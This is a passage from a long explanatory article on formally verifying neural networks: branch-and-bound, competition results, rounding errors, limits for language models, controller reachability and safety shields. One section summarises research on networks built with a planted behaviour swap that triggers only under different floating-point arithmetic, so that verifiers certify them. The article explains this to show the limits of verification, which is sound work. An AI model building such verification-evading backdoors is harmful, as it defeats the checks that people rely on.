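The verifier still has to choose the slope $\lambda$. *Precise Verification of Transformers through ReLU-Catalyzed Abstraction Refinement* (Liu, Zhang and Zhao, 2026) describes a common rule that sets $\lambda$ to 0 or 1, whichever leaves less area between the lines. Here the rule gives 0, and the bound is 1 again. α-CROWN, a refinement, searches for the best slope instead. With $\lambda = 0.25$, the terms in $x$ cancel and $f(x) \le 0.75$. No other slope gives a smaller upper bound, so the claim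 is still unproved.

The remaining step is to split the problem, which verifiers call *branch-and-bound*. If $x \le 0$, both neurons output 0, so $f(x) = 0$. If $x \ge 0$, the first neuron's output is exactly $x$, and only the second needs an approximation. Choosing $\lambda = 0.5$ gives

$$f(x) \;\le\; x - 2 \cdot 0.5\,(x - 0.5) \;=\; 0.5.$$

The bound is at most 0.5 in both halves, which proves the claim. It is also exact, since $f(0.5) = 0.5$. If the claim had been $f(x) \le 0.4$, then $x = 0.5$ would have been a counterexample.

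In a larger network, the verifier keeps splitting until it has proved the property on every piece or found a counterexample. Once it has fixed the sign of every neuron's input on a piece, the network is a weighted sum of its inputs there, and standard methods find its exact maximum. Branch-and-bound is therefore complete for ReLU networks, given enough time.

### Why the worst case takes exponentially long

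One split was enough in the example. But each neuron whose input could be positive or negative can double the number of pieces, so $n$ such neurons can produce $2^n$ pieces. For 300 neurons, that is about $2 \times 10^{90}$.

Good bounds usually settle most pieces early, but no known method avoids this growth for every network. In 2017 Guy Katz and colleagues published Reluplex, an early verifier, and proved that the problem is NP-complete, as Vorobyov and Ilyushin recount. A proposed solution to an *NP-complete* problem is quick to check, but finding one is at least as hard as solving any other problem whose solutions are quick to check. Here the solution is a counterexample, and running the network once checks it.

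The function $f$ from the example helps to explain why. Consider a logic puzzle that asks for a choice of true or false for A, B, C and so on that meets a list of conditions such as "A or B or not C". Represent A by a number $a$ between 0 (false) and 1 (true). On that range $f(a)$ is zero only when $a$ is exactly 0 or 1, so requiring $f(a) = 0$ rules out anything in between. The condition "A or B or not C" fails only when $a = 0$, $b = 0$ and $c = 1$. In that case $\text{ReLU}(c - a - b)$ equals 1, and for every other choice of true and false it equals 0. Now add up one term of each sort for every variable and every condition:

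$$g = f(a) + f(b) + f(c) + \dots + \text{ReLU}(c - a - b) + \dots$$

This network's output is never negative, and it is zero exactly when the inputs solve the puzzle. Proving that $g > 0$ for all inputs therefore means proving that the puzzle has no solution. This problem is decidable, but a verifier that was fast on every ReLU network would also be fast on every such puzzle, and nobody has found a method that fast in half a century of searching.

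The typical case can be much easier than the worst one. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) describes a contest that included 100 of these puzzles, with up to 100 variables each. Four programs solved all of them. The difficulty also depends on how a network represents its function. Another set of questions in the contest came from ReluSplitter, a tool that rewrites a network so that it computes the same outputs but has more neurons of uncertain sign, which makes the same property harder to prove.

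### Local robustness

Researchers most often try to prove *local robustness*, which means that small changes to one particular input don't change the network's answer. Suppose a network gives each class $j$ a score $f_j(x)$, and the input $x_0$ belongs to class $c$. The network is locally robust at $x_0$ with radius $\varepsilon$ if, for every input $x$,

$$\|x - x_0\|_\infty \le \varepsilon \;\Rightarrow\; f_c(x) > f_j(x) \quad \text{for every other class } j.$$

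The left side means that no number in the input changes by more than $\varepsilon$. In a photograph, these numbers are brightness values, usually integers from 0 to 255.

Local robustness is popular partly because it doesn't require anyone to define what a cat looks like, which is hard to specify. It only requires that an almost identical picture get the same label. But proving local robustness at one photograph doesn't show how the network will label another photograph of the same cat from a different angle.

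Some researchers have tried to cover more realistic changes. In one set of questions from the competition, a camera moves or turns slightly while photographing an indoor object. The winning program settled 99 of the 100 questions. However, the movements are on the order of a hundredth of a millimetre and the turns are about 0.00025 degrees, far less than a robot's camera would shake.

Training a network to be easier to verify usually makes it less accurate on ordinary inputs. Ladner and colleagues give figures for networks that sort small photographs into ten categories. One network, trained to resist changes of two brightness steps, labels 83.5% of the test photographs correctly, and a verifier could prove that it labels 66.0% both correctly and robustly. For a network of the same design trained to resist eight steps, the figures are 57.2% and 35.5%. A wider version of the first network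 was more accurate, at 85.4%, but the verifier could prove only 60.3% and left 14% of the photographs unsettled after 1,000 seconds each. The network may be robust on some of those, so the drop from 66.0% to 60.3% could be partly due to the verifier's limits.

### The aircraft collision-avoidance networks

A specification can also define the right answer. The classic example is ACAS Xu, a system that advises unmanned aircraft how to turn to avoid a collision. It uses 45 neural networks, each with 300 neurons and about 13,000 parameters. Each network's five inputs describe the two aircraft, including their speeds and the distance between them. Its five outputs are scores for the possible pieces of advice, and the system gives the one with the lowest score.

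Because each input is a physical quantity, engineers can write down what the network should do in a given situation. Katz and colleagues wrote ten such properties in 2017. Using Reluplex, they proved, for example, that one of the networks advises a strong right turn whenever another aircraft is near and approaching from the left, with exact ranges for "near" and "from the left". This is much more useful than proving local robustness, because it covers every situation in those ranges and the advice is what a pilot would want.

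The same group later applied four of the properties to all 45 networks and the other six to one network each, for a total of 186 cases. Some of the original runs took days, and others never finished. In 2026, Ladner and colleagues allowed each program just under two minutes per case, and three programs resolved all 186. These programs proved the property in 139 cases and found a counterexample in the other 47, about a quarter of the total. Each counterexample gives the designers a specific situation in which the network breaks the rule they wrote down.

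Proving every property would not prove that two aircraft following the advice will stay apart. Each property concerns one piece of advice at one moment, but whether the aircraft stay apart depends on how they fly.

### What verifiers could do in 2026

VNN-COMP, the competition that supplied these results, has compared neural-network verifiers every year since 2020. In July 2026, 11 teams entered 13 programs. Each question consisted of a network, a property and a time limit, and the organisers ran every program on rented computers of equal cost. A correct proof or counterexample earned 10 points, a wrong answer lost 150, and no answer scored zero. Guessing therefore raised a program's expected score only if its guesses were right more than 15 times out of 16. If two programs disagreed, the one that claimed a counterexample had to produce it.

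α,β-CROWN, which combines linear bounds with branch-and-bound, won in 2026, as it has every year since 2021. Its earlier wins include the smaller contest described by Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*. In 2026 it correctly answered 3,164 of the 3,373 questions in the main track (93.8%), with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples.

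The 94% figure applies to these questions, not to neural networks in general. Nearly a third of the questions concern two tiny networks with 4,000 parameters each, and the teams voted on which sets of questions to include. α,β-CROWN answered 38 of the 60 questions in one set, whose proposer deliberately included many hard ones. Its results on six of the 24 sets show how much the difficulty varies.

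| Networks | Parameters | Proved | Counterexample found | Unsettled or wrong |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentence classifiers | 4,000 | 418 | 662 | 0 |
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 139 | 47 | 0 |
| Vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | 123 | 0 | 77 |
| Traffic-sign recognition | 0.9–1.8 million | 0 | 36 | 9 |
| Photographs in 100 categories | 2.5–3.8 million | 127 | 33 | 40 |
| VGG16 | 138 million | 18 | 0 | 0 |

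VGG16, a well-known image network from 2014, has about 1,800 times as many parameters as the larger of the two vision transformers, yet α,β-CROWN resolved every verification query about it. These queries allow small changes to anything from a single pixel to the whole picture. If the changes are small enough, most neurons' inputs keep the same sign throughout, and the network behaves almost like a weighted sum. A network's size is therefore a poor guide to how hard it is to verify. Calling VGG16 "a verified network with 138 million parameters" would also be misleading, because the 18 proofs cover only tiny changes to a few pictures.

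Transformers, the design behind today's language models, are harder for their size because their attention layers multiply together two numbers that both depend on the input. Liu and colleagues explain how verifiers bound such a product with flat planes. If $q$ and $k$ both lie between −1 and 1, then

$$qk \le q - k + 1 \quad\text{and}\quad qk \le k - q + 1.$$

At $q = k = 0$ both planes give 1, although the product is 0. Splitting a ReLU at zero removes its approximation error, but halving the range of $q$ only halves this gap. A verifier may therefore have to split the same product many times. The vision transformers in the competition, which their proposers simplified to make verification possible, have only two or three layers and correctly label only about 60% of ordinary test photographs.

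A program called ACT reported proving all 200 properties of these transformers, 77 more than the winner. This may be a real advance, but the competition results can't confirm it, because the proposers had removed the photographs for which they could find a counterexample. A program that answered "proved" every time would probably have scored just as well. ACT also lost points for ten answers in other sets.

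The organisers penalised eight of the 13 programs, including α,β-CROWN once, for answers that were wrong or came without a valid counterexample. Agate received 955 of these penalties, which its developer attributes partly to a bug in the code that outputs counterexamples. A program can give wrong answers even if the method it implements is sound. The runner-up, Vibecheck, had no penalties and answered 3,108 questions, although its developers had an AI coding tool write it over two months. Its lack of penalties is encouraging, but the organisers can discover a false proof only if another program finds a counterexample. They hope eventually to require each program to output its proofs, which a small separate checker could then confirm.

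Memory is another constraint. For speed, α,β-CROWN works on thousands of pieces of a problem at once, and for each piece it stores a slope $\lambda$ for every neuron that needs one. Vorobyov and Ilyushin measured the memory this takes in June 2026, on a network for recognising handwritten digits whose weights take up 1.5 megabytes. Verification with 4,096 pieces at a time needed about 1.5 gigabytes, a thousand times as much as the weights. They tried splitting the weights between two graphics processors, a standard technique for training large models, but this saved no memory because the slopes took up almost all the space.

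Working on fewer pieces at once reduces the memory needed, to 212 megabytes for 512 pieces, but the verifier then needs more rounds to process the same total. For a larger image network, with 95 megabytes of weights, the slopes took more than 4 gigabytes before any splitting. The competition's graphics processors had at most 24 gigabytes. The two researchers suggest spreading the slopes over many processors as the next step. This might help, but the number of pieces would still grow exponentially.

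### Exact proofs and rounded arithmetic

Most of these proofs treat the network's numbers as exact, but a computer rounds each number to a limited number of digits, so the same sum can have different answers depending on the order of the steps. In standard 64-bit floating-point arithmetic, $2^{53} + 1 - 2^{53}$ comes to 1 if the computer subtracts first, but 0 if it adds first, because $2^{53} + 1$ has one binary digit too many to store. Graphics processors split long sums into parts and add the parts in an order that can change between machines, or even between two runs on one machine.

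Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity (2025) prove in *No Soundness in the Real World* that a verifier can be sound for the exact formula but unsound for the deployed program. Many verifiers allow for rounding by rounding every lower limit down and every upper limit up, so that the limits contain the exact answer. But the deployed program may add the numbers in a different order and get an answer outside those limits.

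The three researchers showed that an attacker could exploit this. For example, an attacker could build the sum above into a network and make the network swap its two classes whenever the sum comes to 0. In exact arithmetic the sum is always 1, so a proof about the exact formula will never reveal the swap. The researchers built networks that change their behaviour when they detect a different order or precision of arithmetic, and every verifier the researchers tested was misled. Running the verifier with more digits wouldn't solve the problem, because the deployed program would still round.

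This matters much less to a company that trained its own network than to one that downloaded a network together with a certificate. Ordinary rounding differences are tiny, so a proof with some margin usually still holds despite them. In the small example above, the proof that $f(x) \le 0.5$ leaves a margin of 0.1 below the claimed 0.6, far larger than any rounding error in so short a calculation. A margin doesn't help against a planted swap, because the attacker decides how large its effect is. Either company could fix the hardware and the order of operations and verify that exact program, though Szász and colleagues argue that verifying what actually runs takes far more computation. They also mention fixed-point arithmetic, which keeps the same number of digits after the point and so has a known limit on its rounding errors.

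Rounding has also caused trouble for the competition. In earlier years the organisers accepted counterexamples that departed from the specification by up to a small tolerance, so one program could prove a property while another refuted it, and both could be right. In 2026 they accepted only inputs that lie exactly within the allowed set, and checked the outputs with one fixed version of the software. Ladner and colleagues acknowledge that this only makes the verdict on borderline cases repeatable, since another computer might still give a different one.

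### What people can prove about language models

A typical language model reads text as *tokens*, which are words or parts of words. With a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens, there are $50{,}000^{10}$, or about $10^{47}$, possible prompts of just ten tokens. Running all of them at a billion per second would take about $3 \times 10^{30}$ years. Agarwal, Faizi and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* that a verifier that can only run the model and look at its answers must, in the worst case, try every prompt, because any prompt it skips might violate the property. To avoid this, a verifier has to use the model's internal structure or choose a set of prompts that it can handle as a group.

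Bound propagation works for small models that classify text. Liu and colleagues tested it on transformers with one to six layers that decide whether a review is positive or negative. They allowed the numbers that represent one word of a review to change slightly and looked for the largest change that provably leaves the model's decision the same. Searching for better bounding planes increased that change by up to 3.6 times for the six-layer models, compared with the best earlier method, but it also increased the average time on film reviews from 11 seconds to 16 minutes. They say transformer verification is still at "a very early stage". A successful proof covers only a small region around a word's numbers, and a synonym may well lie outside it.

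In the competition's sentence classifiers, a language model first converts each sentence into a list of 30 numbers, and a separate network with 128 hidden neurons then decides, for example, whether the user is asking if they are talking to a robot. The verifier checks only the second network. To create the verification problems, researchers rewrote each sentence in many ways, drew the smallest box around the resulting points, and asked whether the second network gives every point in the box the same label. The answer was yes for 418 of the 1,080 boxes. In each of the other 662, some point gets the wrong label, but that point may not correspond to any real sentence. A proof covers every point in the box, but a new wording could fall outside it, so the proof's value depends on how well the box matches what people actually write.

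Agarwal and colleagues propose replacing the transformer with a *weighted automaton*, a simpler model whose properties computer scientists have long had algorithms to check. A weighted automaton has a fixed number of states. Each token moves it between states with certain weights, and the weights along all possible paths determine the number it assigns to the whole text. To build one, the researchers make a table with a row for every possible beginning of a text and a column for every possible ending, and fill in the transformer's output for each combination. If the table is regular enough, a small automaton can approximate it.

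Their construction covers a transformer with a single layer, whereas the language models people use have dozens. The table's size is also a serious obstacle. With 50,000 tokens and beginnings of at most two tokens, it already has 2.5 billion rows and as many columns. The researchers also propose a statistical test that uses only samples from the model to check whether its outputs are close enough to those of an automaton. They measure the distance between the two distributions by adding up the differences in probability over all texts, so rare exceptions are possible even when the distance is small. At a distance of 0.01, the model could produce a forbidden text in one response out of 200 even if the automaton provably never does.

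Instead of proving that a model never breaks a rule, one can calculate how likely it is to do so. A language model assigns a probability $\mu_p(s)$ to each complete response $s$ to a prompt $p$. *BEAVER* (2025) sets out to bound the total probability of the responses that satisfy a constraint $\Phi$:

$$P = \sum_{s} \mu_p(s)\,\mathbf{1}[s \models \Phi].$$

The method explores the most probable beginnings of responses first and adds up the probabilities of the finished responses that satisfy the constraint and, separately, of those that violate it. Suppose the totals so far are 0.90 for responses that satisfy the constraint and 0.03 for those that violate it. The remaining 0.07 belongs to responses not yet checked, so $P$ lies between 0.90 and 0.97. Unlike an estimate from samples, these limits are certain, provided that the calculated probabilities are accurate.

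The method suits short answers best. At any given length, fewer than 1,000 beginnings can each have a probability above 0.001, so a computer can explore them all. But if a model writes 200 tokens and gives each one a probability of 0.9, the whole response has a probability of $0.9^{200}$, or less than one in a billion. For an essay, nearly all the probability would stay unresolved. The proof also covers only one prompt, so it no longer applies if a user adds a comma.

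*Bounded PCTL Model Checking of Large Language Model Outputs* (2025) similarly checks formal properties over a model's most probable continuations. This covers what the model usually writes but leaves out improbable responses, some of which may be dangerous. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) addresses such rare failures. Ordinary sampling is slow for this purpose, since ruling out a failure rate of one in a million takes about three million trials. Engineers in other fields use importance sampling, which generates the rare cases more often and then corrects the estimate to account for this. The paper describes adapting such techniques to language models as an open challenge.

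All of these methods need a specification that a computer can evaluate. A program can check whether a response is valid code, contains a phrase from a list or has fewer than 100 words. Nobody knows how to write such a test for "harmless". The same answer, such as a list of security flaws in a program, may be harmless or dangerous depending on who asked for it. Several harmless answers can also combine into dangerous instructions, which no test on a single response would detect.

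One could instead use a second neural network as a judge and prove that it would approve at least 99% of a model's responses to some prompt. A calculation like BEAVER's could in principle establish this, but the proof would only be about the judge's verdicts. If the judge fails to recognise instructions for making a poison because they are written in an unusual code, they will count as harmless in the proof.

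## Proving that a controller stays safe in its environment

The proofs about the ACAS Xu networks each cover a single piece of advice, but in flight the system gives new advice every second. Researchers check, for example, that the system advises a turn whenever another aircraft is straight ahead and approaching. A network could pass this check every time by alternating between left and right turns, yet the aircraft would keep flying almost straight at the other one. To rule out a collision, a verifier has to follow the whole loop, in which the network's output moves the aircraft and the new position becomes the network's next input.

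### Following every possible state

The *reachable set* $R_t$ contains every state the system could be in after $t$ steps, from all allowed starting states. Let $s$ be a state, such as a position and a speed, and let $\pi(s)$ be the controller's action in that state. The function $f$ describes the dynamics, meaning how the vehicle moves in response, and $w$ is a disturbance, such as wind, from a set $W$. Then

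$$R_{t+1} = \{\, f(s, \pi(s), w) : s \in R_t,\ w \in W \,\}.$$

*Bridging Control with Neural Network Verifier alpha-beta-CROWN* (2026) explains that calculating the exact set of states the system can reach is usually too hard when the controller is a neural network, so verifiers calculate a larger set that is certain to contain it. They first use bound propagation to bound the controller's output over the current set. They then move the set through the dynamics, enlarge it to allow for disturbances and approximations, and check whether it contains any unsafe state. The next step starts from the enlarged set. If none of the sets contains an unsafe state in $T$ steps, the system is safe for that long. If one does, the system may be able to reach an unsafe state, or the set may just be too large.

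Suppose a controller steers a car towards the middle of its lane. Each second it halves the car's distance $x$ from the middle, while gusts of wind move the car by $w$ metres:

$$x' = 0.5x + w.$$

If $x$ starts between −1 and 1 and $|w|$ is at most 0.1, then $x$ lies within ±0.6 after one second, ±0.4 after two and ±0.3 after three. This range tends to ±0.2, where the controller removes as much displacement each second as the gusts can add. But if gusts can in fact move the car by 0.6 metres, the calculation is correct but its assumption about the wind is false, and the car may be 1.1 metres from the middle after the first second, outside the range in which it started.

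The verifier can also introduce errors. The controller's action here is $u = -0.5x$, and the car's next position is $x + u + w$. If the verifier keeps only the range of each term, with $x$ in ±1 and $u$ in ±0.5, it calculates a range of ±1.6 for the next position, then ±2.5 and ±3.85 for the two after that, even though the true range shrinks. As with $x - x$ earlier, the verifier has allowed for combinations that can't occur, such as a car at the right edge that steers further right. The errors accumulate because each step starts from the previous step's enlarged range.

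The verifier can get a tighter estimate by splitting the range. If it cuts ±1 into 20 pieces and handles each separately, the range after one second is ±0.65, close to the true ±0.6. But cutting each of 12 state variables into 20 pieces would produce $20^{12}$ boxes, or about $4 \times 10^{15}$. *The FABRIC Strategy for Verifying Neural Feedback Systems* (2026) names this "curse of dimensionality" as a weakness of reachability analysis. The verifier can also treat several steps as one long formula, which preserves the connection between a position and the action the controller takes there but makes each calculation harder.

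The shape of the sets causes further errors. Many verifiers store each set as a box with sides parallel to the axes, which is quick to compute with. If the dynamics rotate a square by 45 degrees, the smallest such box around it has sides 1.41 times as long. After ten such steps, the box would be 32 times as wide as the original square, although the true set never grew. In *Closing the Loop*, Akinwande, Kochenderfer and Barrett (2026) describe CLIPPER, a verifier that uses such boxes. It took 79 seconds to verify a simple model of a turning car, while CORA, a tool that uses more flexible shapes, took 13. They think the rotation is the likely reason.

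### Safety for unlimited time

A reachability calculation covers only as many steps as the verifier runs, but sometimes a proof about one step covers every step. An *invariant* is a set of states that the system can't leave. In the lane example with gusts of at most 0.1 metres, the range ±1 is an invariant, because a car that starts anywhere in it is within ±0.6 a second later. The same argument applies to every later second.

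A *barrier certificate* is a function $B$ that marks out an invariant between the starting states and the unsafe ones. It has to satisfy

$$\begin{aligned} &B(s) \le 0 \ \text{ for every starting state } s,\\ &B(s) > 0 \ \text{ for every unsafe state } s,\\ &B(s) \le 0 \;\Rightarrow\; B(s') \le 0 \ \text{ for every possible next state } s'. \end{aligned}$$

The system starts where $B$ is zero or negative and can never reach a state where $B$ is positive. Suppose the car is unsafe at 1.5 metres or more from the middle. Then $B(x) = x^2 - 1$ works for the small gusts. It fails for gusts of 0.6 metres, since a car at $x = 1$ could move to 1.1, where $B$ is 0.21. This failure doesn't mean that the car is unsafe, because $B(x) = x^2 - 1.44$ works for the same gusts. A car within 1.2 metres of the middle stays within $0.5 \times 1.2 + 0.6 = 1.2$ metres.

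The verifier has to check only one step, so errors don't accumulate. Finding $B$ is the hard part when the system has many variables and a neural network in the loop. Designers can guess a formula with adjustable numbers, or train a second neural network to act as $B$, and then use a verifier to check the three conditions. How they found $B$ doesn't matter if the check succeeds. However, the guarantee holds for unlimited time only if its assumptions do too. For example, a single one-metre gust could push a car from 1.2 metres out to 1.6.

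### Collisions in the ACAS Xu networks

The designers of an early ACAS Xu prototype used neural networks to compress a huge table of advice for aircraft by a factor of about 1,000. Bak and Tran (2022), in *Neural Network Compression of ACAS Xu Early Prototype is Unsafe*, set out to prove that aircraft following the networks' advice stay apart.

The analysis assumes conditions that favour the system. The sensors are perfect, the aircraft follows all advice exactly and immediately, and the other aircraft flies straight at a constant speed. An encounter begins with the two aircraft more than 60,760 feet (ten nautical miles) apart. Coming within 500 feet horizontally at the same altitude counts as a near mid-air collision.

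Bak and Tran changed the system slightly by rounding each position, speed and heading before passing it to the networks. This left a finite number of possible inputs, so they could run the networks on all of them instead of bounding the outputs. The method works for a network of any size or design, provided that it has few input variables.

They also worked backwards from all possible collisions, which they divided into 1,267,200 groups by position, speed, heading and previous advice. For each group, they calculated exactly which states one second earlier could have led there, and ran the networks to see which of those states would produce the necessary advice. They repeated this until either no earlier states remained, which meant the collision couldn't happen, or they reached a state where the aircraft were still ten miles apart.

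The search usually found a collision in under a minute. When Bak and Tran replayed such cases without the rounding, the aircraft still collided. In one case, a slow aircraft began to turn as soon as a fast one came within range, but too late to avoid it. In a more worrying case, a faster aircraft was coming from behind, and the slower one was already moving out of its path when the system turned it back in. Designers often judge such systems by whether they reduce the total number of near-collisions in simulations, but a system can do this and still cause some that wouldn't otherwise have happened.

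Bak and Tran then limited the aircraft's own speed to between 1,000 and 1,200 feet per second and proved in about 32 minutes that the rounded system has no collisions in that range. At 964 feet per second, they found a collision in the original system. The proof doesn't cover the original networks even at the higher speeds, though it would apply if a manufacturer built the rounding into the aircraft. It also checks for collisions only once a second. Two aircraft approaching head-on at 1,200 feet per second each would cross the 1,000-foot-wide danger zone in under half a second, so they could pass through it between checks. Bak and Tran say that enlarging the sets could close this gap.

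Random testing would have missed many of these cases. Bak and Tran simulated batches of 1.5 million random encounters. When the aircraft flew at the same altitude, a batch contained 17 near-collisions on average. When they started at different altitudes and converged, the average was 0.07, so most batches contained none. They simulated 150 million of these converging encounters in total and found no near-collision in which the aircraft using the system was flying faster than 343 feet per second.

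A related system, VerticalCAS, advises pilots to climb or descend, and whether it can be verified as safe depends on what the verifier assumes about the pilot. *ARCH-COMP26 Category Report* (Sasaki, Wooding and colleagues, 2026), which compares tools for verifying neural-network controllers, includes it as a test problem. In one scenario, the aircraft is descending at 22.5 feet per second. One of the tools, CORA, proved that the aircraft avoids the danger zone for ten seconds if the pilot always chooses the middle of the permitted accelerations, but found a violation if the pilot always chooses the worst.

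### Controllers that use a camera

ACAS Xu receives distances and angles, but many vehicles steer by camera. Verifying a camera-based controller would require a description of every picture the camera could take from each position, and nobody can write a formula for all the pictures that look like a runway.

*Verification of Image-based Neural Network Controllers Using Generative Models* (Sydney Katz, not Guy Katz of Reluplex, with Corso and colleagues, 2021) studies a controller that steers a small aircraft along a runway at 5 metres per second, using a camera on the wing. The researchers replaced the camera with a neural network that generates pictures. They trained a *generative adversarial network* (GAN) on 10,000 pictures from a flight simulator. In a GAN, one network learns to produce pictures that a second network can't distinguish from the originals. The generator takes the aircraft's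 distance from the centre line, its heading, and two numbers that account for other variation, such as which part of the dashed line is in view.

Connecting the generator to the controller makes a single network with four inputs instead of one with an input for every pixel. The researchers divided the possible positions and headings into 16,384 cells, calculated the smallest and largest steering angle in each, and worked out which cells the aircraft could enter next. They proved that the aircraft stays on the runway from any starting position if it starts pointing roughly along the runway. The analysis is inconclusive when the aircraft starts near the edge and points outwards. They also proved that an aircraft starting within 10 degrees of the correct heading gets close to the centre line within 16 seconds. The reachable set is invariant from then on, so the aircraft stays there as long as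 the assumptions hold.

To make this possible, *Scalable Surrogate Verification of Image-based Neural Network Control Systems* (2024) shrinks colour pictures of 200 by 360 pixels to greyscale pictures of 8 by 16, and replaces its first generator with a smaller network that imitates it.

The proof covers every picture that the generator can produce. The generator almost certainly cannot produce every picture that a real aircraft's camera will take, so the proof does not establish that a real aircraft would stay safe. Katz and colleagues think the generator is unlikely to reproduce even its training pictures exactly, and these came from a simulator and show 200 metres of one runway. They therefore measured the distance from each training picture to the closest one that the generator can produce. If the two are close, the controller would plausibly steer in much the same way for both, but a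 neural network can respond very differently to two nearly identical pictures.

One could narrow this gap by proving that the controller also steers safely for every picture within some distance of a generated one, and then checking how often real photographs fall within that distance. The second step would be a statistical estimate, with the same limits as any other test.

Akinwande, Kochenderfer and Barrett (2026), in *Stochastic World Models for Verifying Vision-Based Neural Feedback Systems*, have since applied this approach to a car that brakes for an obstacle, using pictures of 32 by 32 pixels. They divided speeds up to 30 metres per second and distances up to 60 metres into 10,000 cells. With a GAN that produces grey pictures, an earlier method had left 38% of the cells unsettled, but the new one settled all of them, proving 6,536 safe and finding a failure in each of the other 3,464.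 No controller could have avoided most of those failures, because even full braking couldn't stop the car in time from about 32% of the combinations of speed and distance.

That answer is complete, but it applies to a GAN that imitates the camera poorly. On a standard measure of similarity, where identical pictures score 1, the GAN's pictures scored only 0.449 against the simulator's. Akinwande and colleagues also built a better generator for colour pictures, which scored 0.823. Its extra inputs represent physical conditions such as lighting, so an engineer can understand which conditions a range of inputs covers. With this generator they have settled just over 80% of the cells so far. They acknowledge that no formal guarantee connects either generator to a real camera.

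The colour results also use a smaller, less accurate network to estimate distance. Its average error is 38 centimetres, compared with 17 for a larger network with attention layers. In about 10 hours on one graphics processor, Akinwande and colleagues verified 120 cells with the smaller network and only 10 with the larger one.

### How large and how long

Early attempts at this kind of verification often failed because the calculated sets became far too large, according to *Formal Methods in Robot Policy Learning and Verification* (2026). Tools have improved since then, but the problems they can solve are still small. In the 2026 comparison by Sasaki and colleagues, CORA settled 21 of 23 cases, proving 14 and finding violations in 7. The table gives some of its results.

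| System | State variables | Time covered | Result | Computing time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Car following another car | 6 | 5 s | Proved | 3 s |
| Airplane | 12 | 2 s | Violation found | 7 s |
| Quadrotor drone | 12 | 5 s | Proved | 33 s |
| Robot avoiding an obstacle, ordinary training | 4 | 6 s | Proved | 412 s |
| Same robot, robust training | 4 | 6 s | Proved | 2 s |
| Pole balanced on a cart | 4 | 10 s | Proved for a smaller starting range | 227 s |
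| Spacecraft docking | 4 | 40 s | Unsettled | 95 s |

The drone's controller has three layers of 64 neurons, and the proof shows that the drone reaches the right height and stays there for the rest of the five seconds. This result depends on the details of the model and on how well the developers tune the tool. When Akinwande and colleagues tried a version of the drone model that advances in discrete time steps, neither CORA nor their own tool, CLIPPER, could verify it.

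The spacecraft has only a third as many state variables as the drone, but it can start anywhere in a wide region and the proof has to cover 40 seconds. It behaves well in simulations, but the calculated set "explodes". A long duration isn't always an obstacle, though. The braking results cover 238 steps, and the guarantee for the taxiing aircraft has no time limit because its controller steers it back towards the centre line faster than the errors can grow.

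Long proofs can also take a lot of computing time. Settling every cell of the braking problem with grey pictures took 1,043 processor-hours, or about six weeks on a single graphics processor, for a car with two state variables and one stationary obstacle. The results for the two robots in the table suggest that training a controller differently can reduce this time. The developers trained the second controller on whole sets of states instead of single points, and CORA then needed less than a hundredth of the time to verify it.

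## Checking each action before it is carried out

Verifying a controller takes so much computing because the proof has to cover everything the controller might do. A designer can instead leave the controller unverified and check each action it proposes, as AlphaZero's filter does with chess moves. A car needs a more elaborate check. Whether a chess move is legal doesn't depend on what happens next, but holding a steady speed may be harmless now and leave the car unable to stop in time a second later. The check therefore has to look ahead, and the car needs a fallback for when an action fails the check.

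### A simple program that guards a complex one

In 2001 the computer scientist Lui Sha described this arrangement, the *Simplex architecture*. In *Integrate Mixed-Criticality Components with Formalized Architectural Patterns* (2008), he explains it with a sorting problem. Suppose a programmer has a slow sorting program that is proven correct and a fast one that is too complicated to verify. A small verified component lets the fast program rearrange the items in a list but not add, delete or change any. It then checks that the items are in order. If the fast program takes too long or its answer fails the check, the slow program sorts the list instead.

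The final answer is correct whatever the fast program does. Sha points out that even a person could do the sorting. For a million items, the check takes just under a million comparisons, while bubble sort, the slow program in the example, may need about 500 billion. Without the ban on changing items, a program could pass the check by returning "1, 2, 3" for every list.

A command to an aircraft's rudder is harder to mark as right or wrong. Sha's solution is to check whether the command would leave the aircraft in a state that a simple, trusted controller can handle, and to reject the command if it might not. The Boeing 777 has a sophisticated controller for normal flight and a second one based on the 747, whose control methods had been in use for over 25 years. The sophisticated controller should keep the aircraft within the conditions that the second one can manage.

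Sha says designers must verify that faults in the complex software cannot corrupt the checking component or the simple controller, that the simple controller runs in time, and that it works despite every fault the designers have allowed for.

The *Black-Box Simplex* design of Mehmood and colleagues (2021) requires designers to trust only a safety check, not the backup controller. The backup controller proposes a whole sequence of commands, such as braking to a stop. A decision module checks whether the main controller's next command, followed by that sequence, would be safe. If so, the module carries out the command and stores the sequence. If a later check fails, it carries out the stored sequence, which has already passed the check.

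### How early a car has to brake

A *shield* blocks or replaces any action that would break a safety rule. Suppose a shield has to stop a car from hitting a fixed obstacle. A car travelling at 20 m/s (72 km/h), with a delay of 0.5 seconds and braking of 5 m/s², needs $10 + 40 = 50$ metres to stop, by the same formula as for the taxi earlier. The shield can leave the AI in control until the obstacle is 50 metres away, but then it must brake. If the shield checks ten times a second, it must brake at any check where the gap is less than 52 metres, because the car would travel 2 metres before the next check.

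On ice, braking might be only 2 m/s², and the distance becomes $10 + 100 = 110$ metres. A shield that still assumed 5 m/s² would start braking at 50 metres and hit the obstacle at

$$\sqrt{20^2 - 2 \cdot 2 \cdot 40} \approx 15.5 \text{ m/s},$$

or 56 km/h. The proof that the shield works would contain no mistake. It would be a conditional guarantee whose condition, braking of at least 5 m/s², was false.

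### Constructing a shield

*Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, 2017) applied shields to reinforcement learning, in which an AI system learns from rewards by trial and error. Trial and error is dangerous in the real world because the system has to try bad actions to discover that they are bad.

In one of their examples, an agent learns to run a 100-litre hot-water tank cheaply by opening and closing a valve. When the valve is open, between 1 and 2 litres flow in each second. Between 0 and 1 litres flow out each second, whether the valve is open or closed. The tank must never overflow or run dry, and to limit wear, the valve must stay in each new position for at least three seconds.

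The designer supplies the safety rule and an abstract model, a rough description of what could happen next. The model of the tank includes the limits on the flow but not how the heater uses energy, which is what the agent has to learn. A program then looks for the states from which the shield can keep the system safe. It treats the problem as a game in which the environment always makes the worst possible move. In the notation of the previous section, $f(s,a,w)$ is the next state after action $a$ and disturbance $w$. The program starts with the set $K_0$ of all states that obey the rule and repeatedly calculates

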